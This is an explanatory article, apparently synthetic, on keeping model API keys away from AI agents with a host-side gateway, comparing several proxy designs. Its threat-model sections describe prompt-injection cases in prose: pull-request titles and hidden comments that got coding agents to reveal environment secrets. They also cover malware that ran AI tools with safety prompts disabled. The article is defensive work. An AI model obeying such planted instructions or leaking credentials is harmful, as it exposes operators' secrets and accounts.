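# Keeping API credentials away from AI agents with a host-side inference gateway

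## How an AI agent uses an API key, with and without a gateway

An inference gateway is a program that forwards an AI agent's requests to a hosted language model and adds the API key that authorises them and identifies the account to be billed. Operators run the gateway on the host, meaning a trusted machine or process outside the restricted environment where the agent runs. The agent holds no usable key, so it has none to leak if it misbehaves. Most of the design's parts come from ordinary web engineering.

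### What the agent sends to the provider

An agent is a program in which a language model chooses the actions, together with every process the program starts. Claude Code, a coding agent from the AI company Anthropic, reads files, runs shell commands and edits code on a developer's machine. The model itself runs on the provider's servers. The program sends it the conversation so far, and the model replies with either text for the user or a request to run a tool, such as a shell command. The program runs the command, adds the output to the conversation and sends the whole conversation again. One task can take dozens of round trips, and the provider bills for each one.

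Each round trip is an HTTPS request. HTTP, the protocol of the web, divides a request into headers (short labelled lines) and a body, and HTTPS wraps both in TLS, a protocol that encrypts everything between the two ends of the connection. The conversation goes in the body. A header identifies the account to charge. A common form is the word "Authorization", then "Bearer", then the secret; Jones and Hardt (2012), in *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework*, set out the syntax. Anthropic's API accepts the key in a header of its own, so that a request to Claude looks roughly like this:

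```
POST /v1/messages HTTP/1.1
Host: api.anthropic.com
X-API-Key: <the provider key>
```

The provider looks up the key, finds the account and runs the model. It ordinarily checks nothing else about the sender. Under Jones and Hardt's definition, anyone who possesses a bearer token can use it in any way that any other possessor can, without proving possession of a cryptographic key. They were writing about OAuth, a standard for delegating access to web services, but an API key is also a bearer secret, and it works as well from a stranger's laptop as from the developer's. Losing an API key is usually worse than losing an OAuth token, because the sample token in their specification expires after 3,600 seconds, whereas an API key typically works until someone revokes it.

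### One request with the key in an environment variable

The developer usually sets an environment variable, `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY`, and starts the agent from the same terminal. An environment variable is a named value that the operating system gives a process at startup, and which the process passes to its child processes by default.

Before the agent runs, the provider key (the real key, which the provider accepts and bills) is often stored in a shell profile or in a `.env` file in the project directory. Any process running under the developer's account can normally read these files. Formal's *Sandboxing agentic coding tools is a networking problem*, a post by a company that sells access-control proxies, points out that Claude Code can read the directory in which the user launches it. Developers have long kept `.env` files out of version control, but that doesn't stop an agent from reading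 them.

Once the agent starts, the key is in its environment and in that of each subprocess, including the test run, the package installer, and any script the installer downloads and executes. A malicious package can therefore read the key without an exploit. According to Formal, the terminal session's environment variables also pass into the sandbox where Claude Code runs its commands. On Linux, other processes under the same account can generally read these variables too, through `/proc`.

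To make the request, the agent's HTTP library copies the key into memory and writes it into a header. The machine's administrator can read that memory, and so can a debugger running under the same account, if the system permits it. A crash dump or an overly detailed log can save the header to disk. TLS encrypts the request while it crosses the network, and the provider's server decrypts it. This protects the key from eavesdroppers on the network but not from the agent.

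Agents add one more place where the key can end up, the conversation itself, and this can happen without an attack. If the model runs `env` to find out why a build fails, the command prints the key, and the agent adds the output to the conversation. The key is then in the body of every later request in that session and in any transcript the agent saves.

### The parts of a gateway arrangement

**Prompt injection** is text in material the agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction. A model receives its instructions and the material it reads in the same stream of text and cannot reliably tell them apart. Anthropic's guide *Securely deploying AI agents* gives the example of a repository whose README contains unusual instructions that Claude Code then incorporates into its actions. An attacker who succeeds can read whatever the agent can read. Anthropic trains its models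 to resist prompt injection but still advises operators to add controls that do not depend on that training.

A **sandbox** is the container, virtual machine or restricted process in which the agent runs. A container has its own view of files, processes and the network but shares the host's kernel (the core of the operating system), while a virtual machine runs its own kernel. A sandbox limits what the code inside it can access outside, but it doesn't protect a key that the operator has passed in.

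**Egress rules** limit which outside addresses the sandbox can contact. They can help stop a stolen key from leaving the sandbox, but they are coarse. Formal examined the firewall script in Anthropic's template for development containers and found that it allowed connections to any address on port 22, the port for SSH (encrypted remote login). Even without that opening, an agent could put a secret into a package on the npm registry or into a GitHub gist, because the firewall allows access to both sites, which developers need.

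A **proxy** is a program that accepts a request from one party and forwards it to another. The gateway is a proxy that holds the provider key. The server it forwards requests to is called the **upstream**.

**TLS termination** means decrypting an encrypted connection at the proxy. When an agent makes an HTTPS request through an ordinary proxy, the proxy opens a tunnel to the provider and passes along only ciphertext. It can't read the request, so it can't add a header. To do so, it must decrypt the request, using a certificate that the agent trusts, and then re-encrypt it for the provider. The operator can avoid this step by having the agent send requests directly to the gateway over plain HTTP, which many agents allow.

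### The same request through a gateway

The operator starts the gateway outside the sandbox and gives the provider key only to the gateway. Inside the sandbox, `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` contains a local address such as `http://localhost:8080`, and `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY` contains a worthless placeholder, because some software won't start without a key. Formal's worked example uses `sk-ant-dummy` as the placeholder.

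The agent builds its request as before, with the placeholder in the header, and sends it to the local inference endpoint, an address inside the sandbox used in place of the provider's. In the hardened container that Anthropic describes, the sandbox has no network access, so a small relay carries traffic from the local port to a Unix socket, a file-like connection point that the operator has mounted from the host. The gateway listens at the other end. If it allows the request, it replaces the placeholder with the provider key and sends the request to the provider over its own TLS connection. Adding the key after the request has left the agent's control is called credential injection. The provider receives a normal request, and the gateway passes the response back to the agent, whose code needs no change.

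| Place | What it contains | Who can read it |
|---|---|---|
| Key store on the host | Provider key | The operator, the host's administrator, the gateway's account |
| Gateway's memory | Provider key | The host's administrator, the gateway's account |
| Agent's environment, files and subprocesses | Local address and placeholder | The agent and anyone who hijacks it |
| Connection from agent to gateway | Placeholder and conversation, unencrypted | The agent, the gateway, the host's administrator |
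| Connection from gateway to upstream | Provider key, under TLS | The gateway and the provider |

With a gateway, an agent that runs `env` finds the placeholder `sk-ant-dummy` instead of the real key. This protects the real key only if the agent can't access it on the gateway, which a quick local setup can easily get wrong. Formal's demonstration runs mitmproxy, an open-source proxy that decrypts and edits traffic, on the developer's machine with the real key. If the agent runs there under the same account, without a sandbox around the whole agent, it may be able to read the key from the proxy's files or environment. Formal also found that Claude Code required an interactive sign-in before it would read the key variable. Anyone using this setup should check what the sign-in leaves on disk, since a login credential saved inside the sandbox would again expose a real credential to the agent.

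### Holding a key and having it used

With a gateway, the agent no longer has a copy of the key, but it can still make requests that use the key because it needs them to work. The gateway attaches the real key to every request that reaches the local endpoint and passes its checks, whether the developer's task or instructions planted in a README prompted the request.

Someone with a copy of the key can still do much more than someone who controls only an agent that uses it through the gateway. A copy can be used from anywhere, for anything the key permits, until the owner notices and revokes it, and the owner's own systems record none of this use. Someone who controls only the agent has to send each request through the gateway, which can refuse, count and log it. Their access ends when the operator stops the sandbox, but until then they can run up a bill. Security engineers call a component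 a confused deputy when someone without authority induces it to use its own authority for them, and a gateway that forwards every request it receives is easy to exploit this way.

### Older designs that allow use without export

Programmers faced this problem long before language models. In April 1995, Tatu Ylonen, who wrote the original SSH, created the manual page for a companion program, *ssh-agent*. The program holds a user's private keys, and other programs reach it through a Unix socket whose name they find in an environment variable (Ylonen 1995). The "agent" in ssh-agent is the trusted holder of the key, so it corresponds to the gateway here, not to the AI agent. A user can log in to one machine and from there to another without the intermediate machine ever storing a key. According to a later edition of the manual, FreeBSD's *ssh-agent*, the program never sends a private key over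 the channel on which it takes requests.

The protocol was used informally for three decades before the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) published it as a proposed standard in May 2026. According to Miller's *Secure Shell (SSH) Agent Protocol*, its main purpose is to prevent an attacker who gains unprivileged access to the key holder from copying the keys, but this "may not preclude the attacker from stealing use of those keys". The protocol has no authentication of its own, so anyone who can connect can usually obtain a signature. Miller therefore calls for restricting socket access to the owner and authorised delegates, and advises users not to forward the socket to hosts they do not fully trust. The owner can also load a key with a time limit or require a person to confirm each use. Confirmation would be hard to use with an AI agent that makes dozens of model calls per task.

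An SSH private key produces signatures, which can be given to an untrusted program without revealing the key. An API key is a bearer secret, so it has to be sent with the request. A trusted component that withholds the key from an untrusted program must therefore send the request itself, so the equivalent of ssh-agent for API keys is a proxy.

The security company CyberArk built Secretless Broker mainly for databases. Walsh's *Introducing the Secretless Broker Open Source Beta* describes it as a separate local process that supplies credentials for an application's connections. Code Climate's *Line length* (2018), an automated style check of the announcement's source file, dates the announcement to 3 September 2018. In the PostgreSQL demonstration in CyberArk's *Secretless Broker*, the project's documentation, a direct connection without a password fails, but a passwordless connection through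 the broker's port succeeds because the broker fetches the credentials and completes the login. In CyberArk's laptop benchmark, using the broker reduced throughput by about a tenth (from 272 transactions per second to 245), though the same document elsewhere puts the loss at about 25 per cent. Model calls commonly take seconds, so a comparable delay would hardly be noticeable.

CyberArk also claims that with the broker in place the client "is not part of the threat surface". This is true of the password, which the client can no longer reveal, but not of the data. In the demonstration, anyone who can reach the broker's port can read the tables. That includes a compromised application, because the application is meant to connect through the broker.

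Fly.io, a hosting company, came closest to the present arrangement with Tokenizer, whose code repository dates from 14 April 2023 according to Ecosyste.ms' *Tokenizer*, an index entry for the project. As the company explains in *Tokenized Tokens*, it already kept customers' secrets in a vault, a service that stores secrets encrypted and controls who may fetch them. But most secrets for outside services are bearer tokens, which an application has to read into memory before sending. "If good code can read a secret from Vault, so can a YAML vulnerability", the company writes, meaning a flaw that lets an attacker run code through a configuration file. Fly.io therefore encrypted each secret so that only Tokenizer, a small HTTP proxy, could decrypt it. The main application stores the ciphertext and attaches it to a request, and the proxy decrypts it and writes the real secret into the header. An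 attacker in control of the application could still direct the request to their own server and collect the secret there, so Tokenizer can bind each secret to a list of permitted hosts. A gateway for model requests needs the same restriction, but can enforce it more simply by fixing the upstream in its configuration.

Anthropic's deployment guide recommends the pattern for agents, with a proxy outside the agent's security boundary. The agent sends requests without credentials, and the proxy adds the credentials and forwards the requests. Other benefits Anthropic lists include a single place to store keys, a log of all requests and control over which endpoints the agent may call. The guide describes the same setup for containers, for virtual machines with no outside network interface, and for cloud deployments whose firewall blocks all traffic except to the proxy. It identifies systems that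 serve several customers and agents that handle untrusted content as the cases where the proxy is useful. It does not prescribe the proxy for everyone, because a developer on a laptop has different needs from a company that processes customers' data.

The guide is a vendor's engineering advice and reports no attacks against the arrangement, so it shows that the pattern is recommended practice but not how secure a given build is. It warns that even read-only access to a code directory can expose credentials, and Anthropic's list of files to exclude begins with `.env`. In the walk-through above, if the operator moves the key into a gateway but then mounts a project that still contains the old `.env` file, the agent has access to the real key as well as the placeholder.

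## Deciding which attacks the gateway has to stop

No gateway protects its key from every attacker. A gateway in a separate container can stop a malicious package in the sandbox from reading the key, but it can't stop the person who administers the machine. Before building anything, an operator therefore needs a threat model, which lists the attackers the system has to withstand, what each can already do, and which attackers the operator has decided not to resist.

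The list of adversaries in Ganesan's *Agent Authenticator* (2026) fits a host-side gateway well. The paper proposes hardware-held keys for agents, a design Ganesan has not fully built, and treats the agent and everything it starts as untrusted. Three of its adversaries apply directly: someone who controls text the agent reads, malicious code running on the same host with the same user's privileges, and someone who operates a server the agent contacts. The paper also considers someone who has tampered with a cloud sandbox's software image, which a gateway builder can treat as malicious code inside the sandbox. It leaves out anyone with administrator rights on the developer's machine, but a gateway builder should include them because the key is now stored on a host that somebody administers.

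### What each attacker gains

| Attacker | Gain if the agent holds the key | Gain if the gateway holds the key | Section that deals with the remainder |
|---|---|---|---|
| Author of text the agent reads | A copy of the key, if the agent obeys and has some way to send it out | Model calls at the operator's expense while the sandbox runs; the key only if a response or error message contains it | "Limiting what an agent can do through the gateway"; "Keeping the key out of what the agent gets back" |
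| Malicious code beside the agent | A copy of the key, straight from a file or the environment | The same model calls; the key only if the code can reach the gateway's files, memory or account | "Setting up the local inference endpoint"; "Storing the key and protecting the gateway" |
| Hostile server the agent contacts | Any key the agent sends to it | The placeholder and whatever else the agent sends; the key only if the gateway adds it to requests for that server | "Choosing where the key is added to a request" |
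| Administrator of the host | A copy of the key | A copy of the key, from the gateway's memory or its key store | "Storing the key and protecting the gateway", which can only reduce the number of such people |

One person can play several of these roles. Someone who writes a README can persuade an agent to install a package that runs their code in the sandbox. A hostile server can return text that the agent reads. An operator who plans for only one role should check that the same attacker can't get in through another.

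The third column assumes that the sandbox holds and that the gateway runs outside it under a separate account.

### Text written by strangers

In 2026 the security engineer Aonan Guan, with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University, published an attack he called Comment and Control. According to SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection*, it worked on three agents that run in GitHub Actions, GitHub's service for automated jobs: Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, Google's Gemini CLI Action and GitHub's Copilot Agent. To attack Anthropic's agent, the researchers put instructions in the title of a pull request (a proposed change to the code). The agent read the title as part of its review, ran commands, and published credentials as a security finding or in the job's log. The researchers obtained a full API key from Google's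 agent using an issue title and comments.

In each case, the agent read outsiders' text and had shell access in the same runtime that held the secret. The stolen credentials then left through GitHub comments and logs. Egress rules would have made little difference, since a job that reviews pull requests must reach GitHub.

A gateway would have kept the model API keys out of these jobs, so the agent could have published only a placeholder in their place. It would not have protected other credentials in the jobs, such as the `GITHUB_TOKEN` that a GitHub Actions job commonly has, which lets it act on the repository. An attacker could still have used the pull-request title to steer the agent into running commands.

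The demonstrated attack needs a workflow that gives the agent secrets even when a pull request comes from a fork (an outsider's copy of a repository). GitHub Actions withholds secrets from such pull requests by default, according to OODA Loop's *Three AI coding agents leaked secrets through a single prompt injection*. For Copilot, the victim also had to assign the attacker's issue to the agent by hand.

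Nobody knew how often anyone tried this outside a laboratory until Nakibly and Babo (2026), in *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, searched 142.7 million GitHub issues, pull requests and comments. They looked for text that GitHub does not display but that an agent receives, mostly in HTML comments. After sorting it with two language models, they reviewed the remaining 5,251 items by hand and found 43 attacks, about one in 3.3 million of the items searched. Nineteen of the attacks tried to steal secrets from the agent's environment, for example by asking the agent to print its environment variables or read `.env` files.

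The average rate is low, but the attacks were not evenly spread. Of the 43 attacks, 24 addressed a specific agent that the project ran, and 19 were in repositories belonging to large AI or cloud companies. Nine named the agent's actual tools or output fields, which the attacker could have learned only by reading the project's workflow. An agent that answers issues on a well-known public project is therefore much more exposed than one that works on a private repository. The count is also a minimum, because Nakibly and Babo excluded instructions in visible titles, which is where Guan put his.

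### Code running beside the agent

Malicious code can steal credentials without involving the model. On 26 August 2025, attackers published altered versions of Nx, a build system for JavaScript projects with around six million weekly installs. Choda, of the NHI Mgmt Group, describes a post-install script that searched the machine for GitHub and npm tokens, SSH keys, cloud credentials and AI tool configuration. The script then uploaded what it found to the victim's GitHub account, in a public repository whose name contained "s1ngularity-repository". The secrets were in ordinary files and environment variables that any process under the developer's account could read.

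GitGuardian's *The Nx s1ngularity attack* (2025), an analysis by a company that sells secret-detection software, counted 2,349 distinct secrets. The most common types were credentials for GitHub, npm, AWS and OpenAI, and about half still worked when the company checked. The body of the analysis shows that 1,079 repositories contained at least one secret. GitGuardian's summary, and often other accounts of the case, give this figure as the number of machines the secrets came from. The number of machines is probably close to that, but GitGuardian did not measure it separately.

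The script also ran AI command-line tools already on the machine, including Claude, Gemini and Amazon Q, to help find sensitive files, using flags that switch off their safety prompts. GitGuardian reports that only 95 of the 366 systems where this happened produced the inventory file the script requested. It attributes many of the failures to the tools refusing, but gives no count of refusals. The attackers still collected secrets in bulk because their script also searched for them directly.

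Whether a gateway would have protected an OpenAI key in this case depends on where the installation ran. Inside a sandbox, the script would have found a placeholder. Under the developer's own account, it could have read the real key if the gateway kept it in a file there. According to the security company Wiz, quoted in SecurityWeek, the malware often ran on developers' machines, in many cases through the Nx extension for VS Code, and sometimes in build pipelines. An editor extension normally runs outside any sandbox the developer has set up for an agent, so a builder who wants to withstand this attack needs to run the gateway under a separate account or on another machine.

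Two days later, the attackers used the stolen GitHub tokens to make private repositories public. GitGuardian counted 10,767 of these repositories and found 82,901 more secrets in the exposed code, 11,168 of them valid. Moving only the model key behind a gateway would have protected that key in the first theft, but not the other secrets taken with it.

Attackers have kept using this method. Help Net Security's *Check your GitHub repos* (2026) describes a campaign that began on 10 November 2026, in which someone with stolen GitHub credentials pushed malicious code into tens of thousands of repositories. The code ran in more than 1,800 of them and sent secrets to the attacker. It looked for OpenAI, Anthropic, Cursor and Copilot tokens as well as cloud credentials, so such programs now routinely collect AI keys. It also deleted the logs and the record of its run within about a minute. A gateway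 on a different machine would at least keep its own record of the model requests the code made through it.

### Hostile servers and administrators

An agent that holds the real key sends it to the provider address in its settings. If an attacker changes `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` to point to their own server, the agent's next request sends them the key. If the agent holds a placeholder instead, the attacker receives only the placeholder and the conversation, which may contain source code or customers' data. The operator needs egress rules to prevent the agent from sending the conversation to the attacker.

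A secret can also leak through a request that has nothing to do with the model. The Hacker News' *RoguePilot Flaw in GitHub Codespaces Enabled Copilot to Leak GITHUB_TOKEN* (2026) reports a flaw that Orca Security found in Codespaces, GitHub's hosted development environment. The token was in an internal file that Copilot could read, and it reached an outside server through a request for a remote JSON schema, a file that describes how other files should be structured. Microsoft has since fixed the flaw. A gateway protects against leaks like this one only for keys that the operator has moved to it, because the files the agent can read then contain no usable key.

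If the agent can choose the upstream, the gateway itself can expose the credential by sending it to a host the agent chose, so Fly.io's Tokenizer has a list of permitted hosts.

An administrator of the gateway's host can read the key under any design. Moving the gateway from a laptop to a company server means that the server's administrators can read the key instead of the laptop's, which is an improvement if there are fewer of them. The operator should also check that the agent doesn't already have administrator access. A developer may run an agent without a sandbox on an account that can use `sudo` without a password. A container may have access to the host's Docker socket, which lets a process start another container with the host's files mounted. In both cases, an attacker who plants instructions in a README can gain administrator access to the host.

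Ganesan objects to proxies because the secret remains a bearer token. He would prefer a separate key for each agent and service, held in hardware that never releases it. If a service doesn't accept such keys, his design falls back on a broker that obtains an ordinary token and never shows it to the model, much like a gateway. When a provider accepts only API keys, a builder has little choice but to store the bearer secret somewhere and protect that place.

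### How often credentials leak from agents

The cases above involved an attacker, but many leaks begin with careless code. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied skills, which are packages of written instructions and scripts that extend what an agent can do. They randomly sampled 17,022 of the 170,226 skills on the SkillsMP marketplace and used keyword and code analysis to narrow these to 3,156 candidates. They ran each candidate with Claude Code in a container with uniquely marked fake credentials. Each ran three times on ordinary tasks and three times with hostile instructions in the material it processed. Three reviewers classified the 1,427 skills that behaved suspiciously.

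The study found 520 affected skills, or 3.1 per cent of the sample. Reviewers judged 83 of these malicious and 437 negligent. The negligent skills contained 1,371 issues, and 73.5 per cent of those came from code that printed sensitive values, usually debugging statements developers had forgotten to remove. The agent adds this output to the conversation, just as it adds the output of `env`, so anyone who can question the agent can obtain the token.

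Chen and colleagues call 466 of the 520 affected skills (89.6 per cent) exploitable because they exposed a credential through some channel while running, which is a broader standard than theft. In 394 skills, a credential appeared in the program's output, and an attacker would still need access to the conversation to use it. Sixty-eight skills sent credentials to an attacker's server. The 3.1 per cent figure also applies to only one marketplace, and could be too low even there, because the keyword search removed about half of the sample before any skill ran and the code analysis followed secrets only within single functions in Python and JavaScript.

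With a gateway, a skill that prints the model key prints only a placeholder. The gateway doesn't protect skill authors' own credentials, which are hardcoded in 107 skills, or the keys that users supply for other services.

There are many of those other keys. Many agents reach outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common format for asking a separate program, called an MCP server, to do things such as read a database or update an issue tracker. Ganesan cites a survey of 5,205 open-source MCP servers in which 88 per cent required credentials, 53 per cent relied on static API keys or personal access tokens, and 8.5 per cent used OAuth, which can issue tokens that expire. The survey covered published code to find what kind of credential the servers expect, so it doesn't measure how many servers have leaked one or how many people use each server.

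GitGuardian counted 28.65 million secrets newly leaked on public GitHub in 2025, a figure Ganesan also cites, with leaks of AI-service credentials up 81 per cent. The company found 24,008 secrets in MCP configuration files, but only 2,117, about 9 per cent, were valid. GitGuardian has a commercial interest in large totals, and the number of valid secrets is the better guide to what an attacker could use. Neither number shows how the secrets got into the files or whether an agent was involved.

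A count by another vendor, Apiiro, does show how the secrets leaked. When a user of Claude Code approves a command and chooses not to be asked again, the program saves the exact command, including any password in it, to a settings file in the project folder. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub* reports that Apiiro found such files in 103,617 public repositories, and 2,539 secrets in 1,994 of them. AI model keys were among the most common types. The developers published the files themselves, so the leaks required no attack. A gateway keeps the model key out of the sandbox, so the key can't end up in a command there unless someone pastes it into a prompt.

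### Telling the model to keep the secret

An operator could instead leave the key where it is and instruct the agent not to reveal credentials. This is easy and sometimes works, as the refusals in the Nx case suggest. But whether a model follows that instruction or an attacker's depends on the model and the wording. Nakibly and Babo replayed their 43 attacks offline against five models acting as the targeted agents, and one small, fast model carried out 19 per cent of them. Operators often use such models to sort issues because they are cheap. None of the attacks worked once the researchers had stripped out the HTML comments. Stripping comments is worthwhile, but it wouldn't remove an instruction in a visible title.

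Google responded to Comment and Control with an instruction of this kind. Guan told SecurityWeek that Google had added "guardrail prompts" to the agent's system prompt, and that the threat was unchanged because the agent kept the same tools. Anthropic instead blocked one command, `ps`, which lists running processes. Guan thinks the attack still works in principle with a different payload, although he did not attempt a full bypass after the fix. Both companies left the key where the agent could get it and tried to make the agent less likely to do so.

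Instructions also can't prevent leaks that don't involve a decision by the model. An installation script can read the environment without going through the model, and a forgotten debugging line prints a token regardless of the system prompt. Ganesan lists safeguards that run inside the agent as a recurring cause of failure in the incidents he examined, because whatever subverts the agent can subvert them too. A model's tendency to withhold secrets is a useful extra layer, but an operator shouldn't rely on it when working out who could obtain the key.

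### When a gateway is not worth its cost

A gateway is one more service to configure, patch and monitor, and if it goes down, every agent behind it stops working. It also gathers keys in one place, and gateway software has its own vulnerabilities, which "Storing the key and protecting the gateway" covers.

Suppose a developer's API key expires tonight and the provider cuts it off after $20 of spending. The agent works on the developer's own code, installs no new packages and doesn't browse the web. A thief could get at most $20 of model use, plus anything else the key gives access to, such as stored files or past requests on some accounts. If the key gives access to nothing else, the possible loss doesn't justify the time needed to set up a gateway. The developer could reasonably use a separate capped key for each project instead.

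The spending limit matters more here than the expiry. GitGuardian says attackers can use stolen credentials within two to four hours, so a key that lasts a day leaves them enough time. The provider must also enforce the limit, because an email warning arrives after the money is gone.

Trusted input is hard to guarantee. Nx was a popular, legitimate tool, and the developers who installed the malicious versions had no particular reason to distrust it. An agent allowed to run `npm install` is exposed to code from every author in the dependency tree, so a developer who relies on trusted input should pin the versions already in use and stop the agent from adding others.

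A gateway is usually worth having when several agents share a company key with a high limit, or when an agent reads issues that anyone can file. Comment and Control shows why even a well-resourced vendor's agent needs one. If an agent runs unsandboxed on a developer's laptop, sandboxing should come first, because a gateway running under the same account as the agent leaves the key about as easy to steal as before.

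## Choosing where the key is added to a request

After deciding to run a gateway, an operator has to choose where the key is added to a request. The agent's software can call the gateway's address instead of the provider's, or it can call the provider as usual while a proxy or the network changes the request on the way. Other designs drop the shared API key and either give the agent a short-lived credential or let it use a signing key that never leaves a chip.

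One request is enough to compare the places where the key can be added. A coding agent in a sandbox uses Claude to explain a failing test. Its `POST /v1/messages` request, with the test output in the body, has to reach `api.anthropic.com` and be billed to someone's account.

### Calling the gateway's own address

Most software that calls a model API has a base URL setting, such as `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, that the operator can point at the gateway. OpenShell works this way (see "Setting up the local inference endpoint"), as do the Agent Gateways from Runloop, a company that hosts sandboxes.

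The operator stores the Anthropic key on Runloop's servers and writes a gateway configuration that specifies the target, `https://api.anthropic.com`, and how to attach the key. When the operator creates a devbox with this configuration, Runloop sets two environment variables in it, `ANTHROPIC_URL` with the gateway's address and `ANTHROPIC` with a gateway token. Claude Code reads different variables, so the operator copies the values into those. The agent sends its question about the test to the gateway with the token in the header. The gateway replaces the token with the real key and forwards the request to Anthropic.

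A gateway token is a limited credential that the gateway accepts and the provider doesn't. A dummy key such as `sk-ant-dummy` is the same for everyone, so a gateway that accepts it depends on the network to restrict who can reach its port. With tokens, the gateway can tell sandboxes apart and revoke one sandbox's access. Runloop binds each token to a single devbox and claims that it won't work from any other machine. A builder can check this by copying a token into a second sandbox and sending a request with it. Any process inside the token's own devbox can still use it. CapSeal, covered in "Limiting what an agent can do through the gateway", narrows what such a credential permits.

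The operator has to trust whoever runs the gateway, which is another company in Runloop's case. But this design needs no TLS interception, because the agent connects to the gateway under the gateway's own name. For the same reason, it rarely has problems with certificate pinning, where a program accepts only the certificates it was built to expect.

Software without a base URL setting won't work. Runloop's gateway needs the token in the first request, so clients that send a password only after the server requests one, as some package managers do, won't work either. An agent that signs in through OAuth, with a browser login instead of a key, usually contacts login addresses that the base URL setting doesn't cover.

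If the agent writes a script that ignores the setting and calls `api.anthropic.com` directly, the script sends Anthropic the gateway token and gets an authentication error, which is easy to notice. But if the project still contains an old `.env` file with a real key, the direct request succeeds and the gateway has no record of it. Egress rules that block the provider's address make that request fail with a connection error. Runloop recommends such rules and provides a switch, `allow_agent_gateway`, to let gateway traffic through them. Adding Runloop's hostnames to the list of allowed sites doesn't have the same effect.

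Changing the key can also cause failures. Runloop gives an updated secret to new devboxes, so model calls from devboxes already running will probably fail once the operator revokes the old key at Anthropic.

### Swapping a placeholder on the way out

Docker Sandboxes runs coding agents in isolated environments on a developer's machine. The agent keeps calling the provider's normal address, and a proxy on the host changes the request. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes the process, which for the question about the failing test goes like this:

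1. The developer runs `sbx secret set anthropic` on the host and types the key at a prompt. Docker saves it in the operating system's keychain if there is one.
2. In the sandbox, the agent has only a sentinel, a meaningless string such as `proxy-managed`, where the key would be.
3. The agent opens an HTTPS connection to `api.anthropic.com` and sends the sentinel in the header.
4. The proxy intercepts the request and checks whether its destination belongs to a service declared in the agent's kit, the package that tells Docker how to run the agent.
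5. The proxy fetches the key, overwrites the header that the kit specifies, and sends the request on over its own TLS connection.

The sentinel plays no part in the matching. The proxy adds the real credential whatever the environment variable contains.

Overwriting the header also blocks one way to steal data. An attacker can plant instructions that tell the agent to upload files to the provider under the attacker's API key, and egress rules will allow the upload because the agent needs access to that address. If the proxy replaces the attacker's key with the operator's, the files go to the operator's account. But the proxy has to cover every header that can carry a key. According to Anthropic's *Authentication*, the API accepts a key in either `Authorization` or the older `x-api-key`, so a proxy that writes one should delete the other.

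#### Which requests get the key

Docker matches requests by service, and each service has a list of hosts. The proxy picks the key according to the address the agent calls, so an agent that uses several model providers needs no extra setting. The `anthropic` service covers four hosts, including the API and `claude.ai`, and the `openai` service covers `chatgpt.com`. A gateway built only for model calls can use a much shorter list. Docker's `github` list, however, omits `npm.pkg.github.com`, so an agent can't install a private package from there until the developer adds a separate secret for that host.

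Secrets are global by default, so every sandbox can use them. The developer can limit a secret to one sandbox with `--sandbox`, and it takes precedence there over the global secret. If the developer later removes it, Docker goes back to the global secret, so removing a sandbox's own key to cut off its access may instead give it the shared company key. Changes now reach running sandboxes without a restart. According to an earlier edition of Docker's *Manage credentials*, a changed global secret applied only to newly created sandboxes, so anyone replacing a leaked key on an older installation should check whether running sandboxes receive the new one.

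The proxy adds credentials only to HTTPS requests. If a script calls a plain `http://` address, the proxy forwards the request with the sentinel still in it, because adding the key would expose the key to anyone on the network path. The proxy doesn't remove credentials that the program put in a plain HTTP request.

Kits from outside Docker need the user's approval for each credential and each host. In an automated job, nobody can answer the approval prompt, so the sandbox starts without the credential, and Docker prints a warning if the kit marked it as required. The proxy then strips the authentication headers from the affected requests, and the developer sees the provider reject them for lack of a key, even though the store holds a valid key.

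#### What breaks when a proxy decrypts the traffic

Because the proxy terminates TLS, the sandbox has to trust a certificate authority that the proxy controls. Anyone who obtains that authority's private key can impersonate any website to the sandbox. The proxy can also read all the traffic it decrypts, including credentials for unrelated services.

A program with certificate pinning rejects the proxy's certificate and reports a TLS error before it sends the request. Some programs without pinning fail the same way because they use their own list of certificate authorities instead of the operating system's. Node.js and Java do this by default, so the builder has to add the proxy's authority to their lists separately. A program that identifies itself with a client certificate also fails, because the proxy can't present that certificate without its private key.

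Some agents check the format of the key when they start. For these, Docker has an experimental feature called custom secrets, which lets the developer choose a placeholder that will pass the check. The proxy finds the placeholder and replaces it with the real key, but only in headers that the developer has named or the default settings cover. The earlier edition replaced it anywhere in the request, including the body, which creates a danger explained in "Keeping the key out of what the agent gets back".

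OAuth logins need their own handling because the login server's reply contains a real token. For supported agents, Docker keeps this token on the host and gives the sandbox a sentinel. If a kit sets `passthrough: true`, the agent receives the real token instead. The earlier edition warned that logging in from a sandbox running a third-party kit would store the real token in that sandbox. Anyone who reviews a Docker setup should look for this setting and for logins made in sandboxes running third-party kits.

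SSH isn't HTTP, so Docker forwards the host's ssh-agent into the sandbox instead.

A thief in the sandbox gets the sentinel and can make model calls until the sandbox stops.

### Redirecting traffic without the agent's cooperation

A program normally uses a proxy only if it reads a setting such as the `HTTP_PROXY` environment variable. Some programs ignore these settings, and an agent can write and run one at any time. LangChain, which makes tools for building agents, avoids this problem by controlling the sandbox's network. *How Auth Proxy secures network access for LangSmith agent sandboxes* (Loganathan, 2026) describes a proxy that all outbound requests pass through, whether or not the program is configured to use it.

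*API Key Security for AI Agents*, by Sandbox0, which also sells sandboxes, explains the mechanism in more detail. The agent sends an ordinary request with no credential. The Linux firewall on the host diverts the connection to a program called netd before it leaves the machine. netd looks up the destination in the sandbox's rules, fetches the matching secret and adds it to the request's headers. In the failing test example, Claude Code would call `api.anthropic.com` with its usual settings, and netd would add the Anthropic key.

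The advantage of this over placeholders is compatibility. Sandbox0 says the improvement is that the agent has "no fake credential to steal", but stealing a worthless string does no harm. The compatibility gain is smaller than it sounds, because software that refuses to start without a key still needs a placeholder. For HTTPS, netd also terminates TLS and opens a second connection, as Docker's proxy does, although Sandbox0 describes the injection as taking place entirely at the kernel's network layer. The sandbox must trust netd's certificate, so programs with certificate pinning still fail.

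As Sandbox0 also argues, a compromised agent could bypass a gateway that depends on a base URL setting. It would then have no working key, so it would gain nothing from the bypass unless it could find a real key elsewhere. Forced redirection is more useful for controlling where the agent's data goes, and egress rules can do that with any of these designs.

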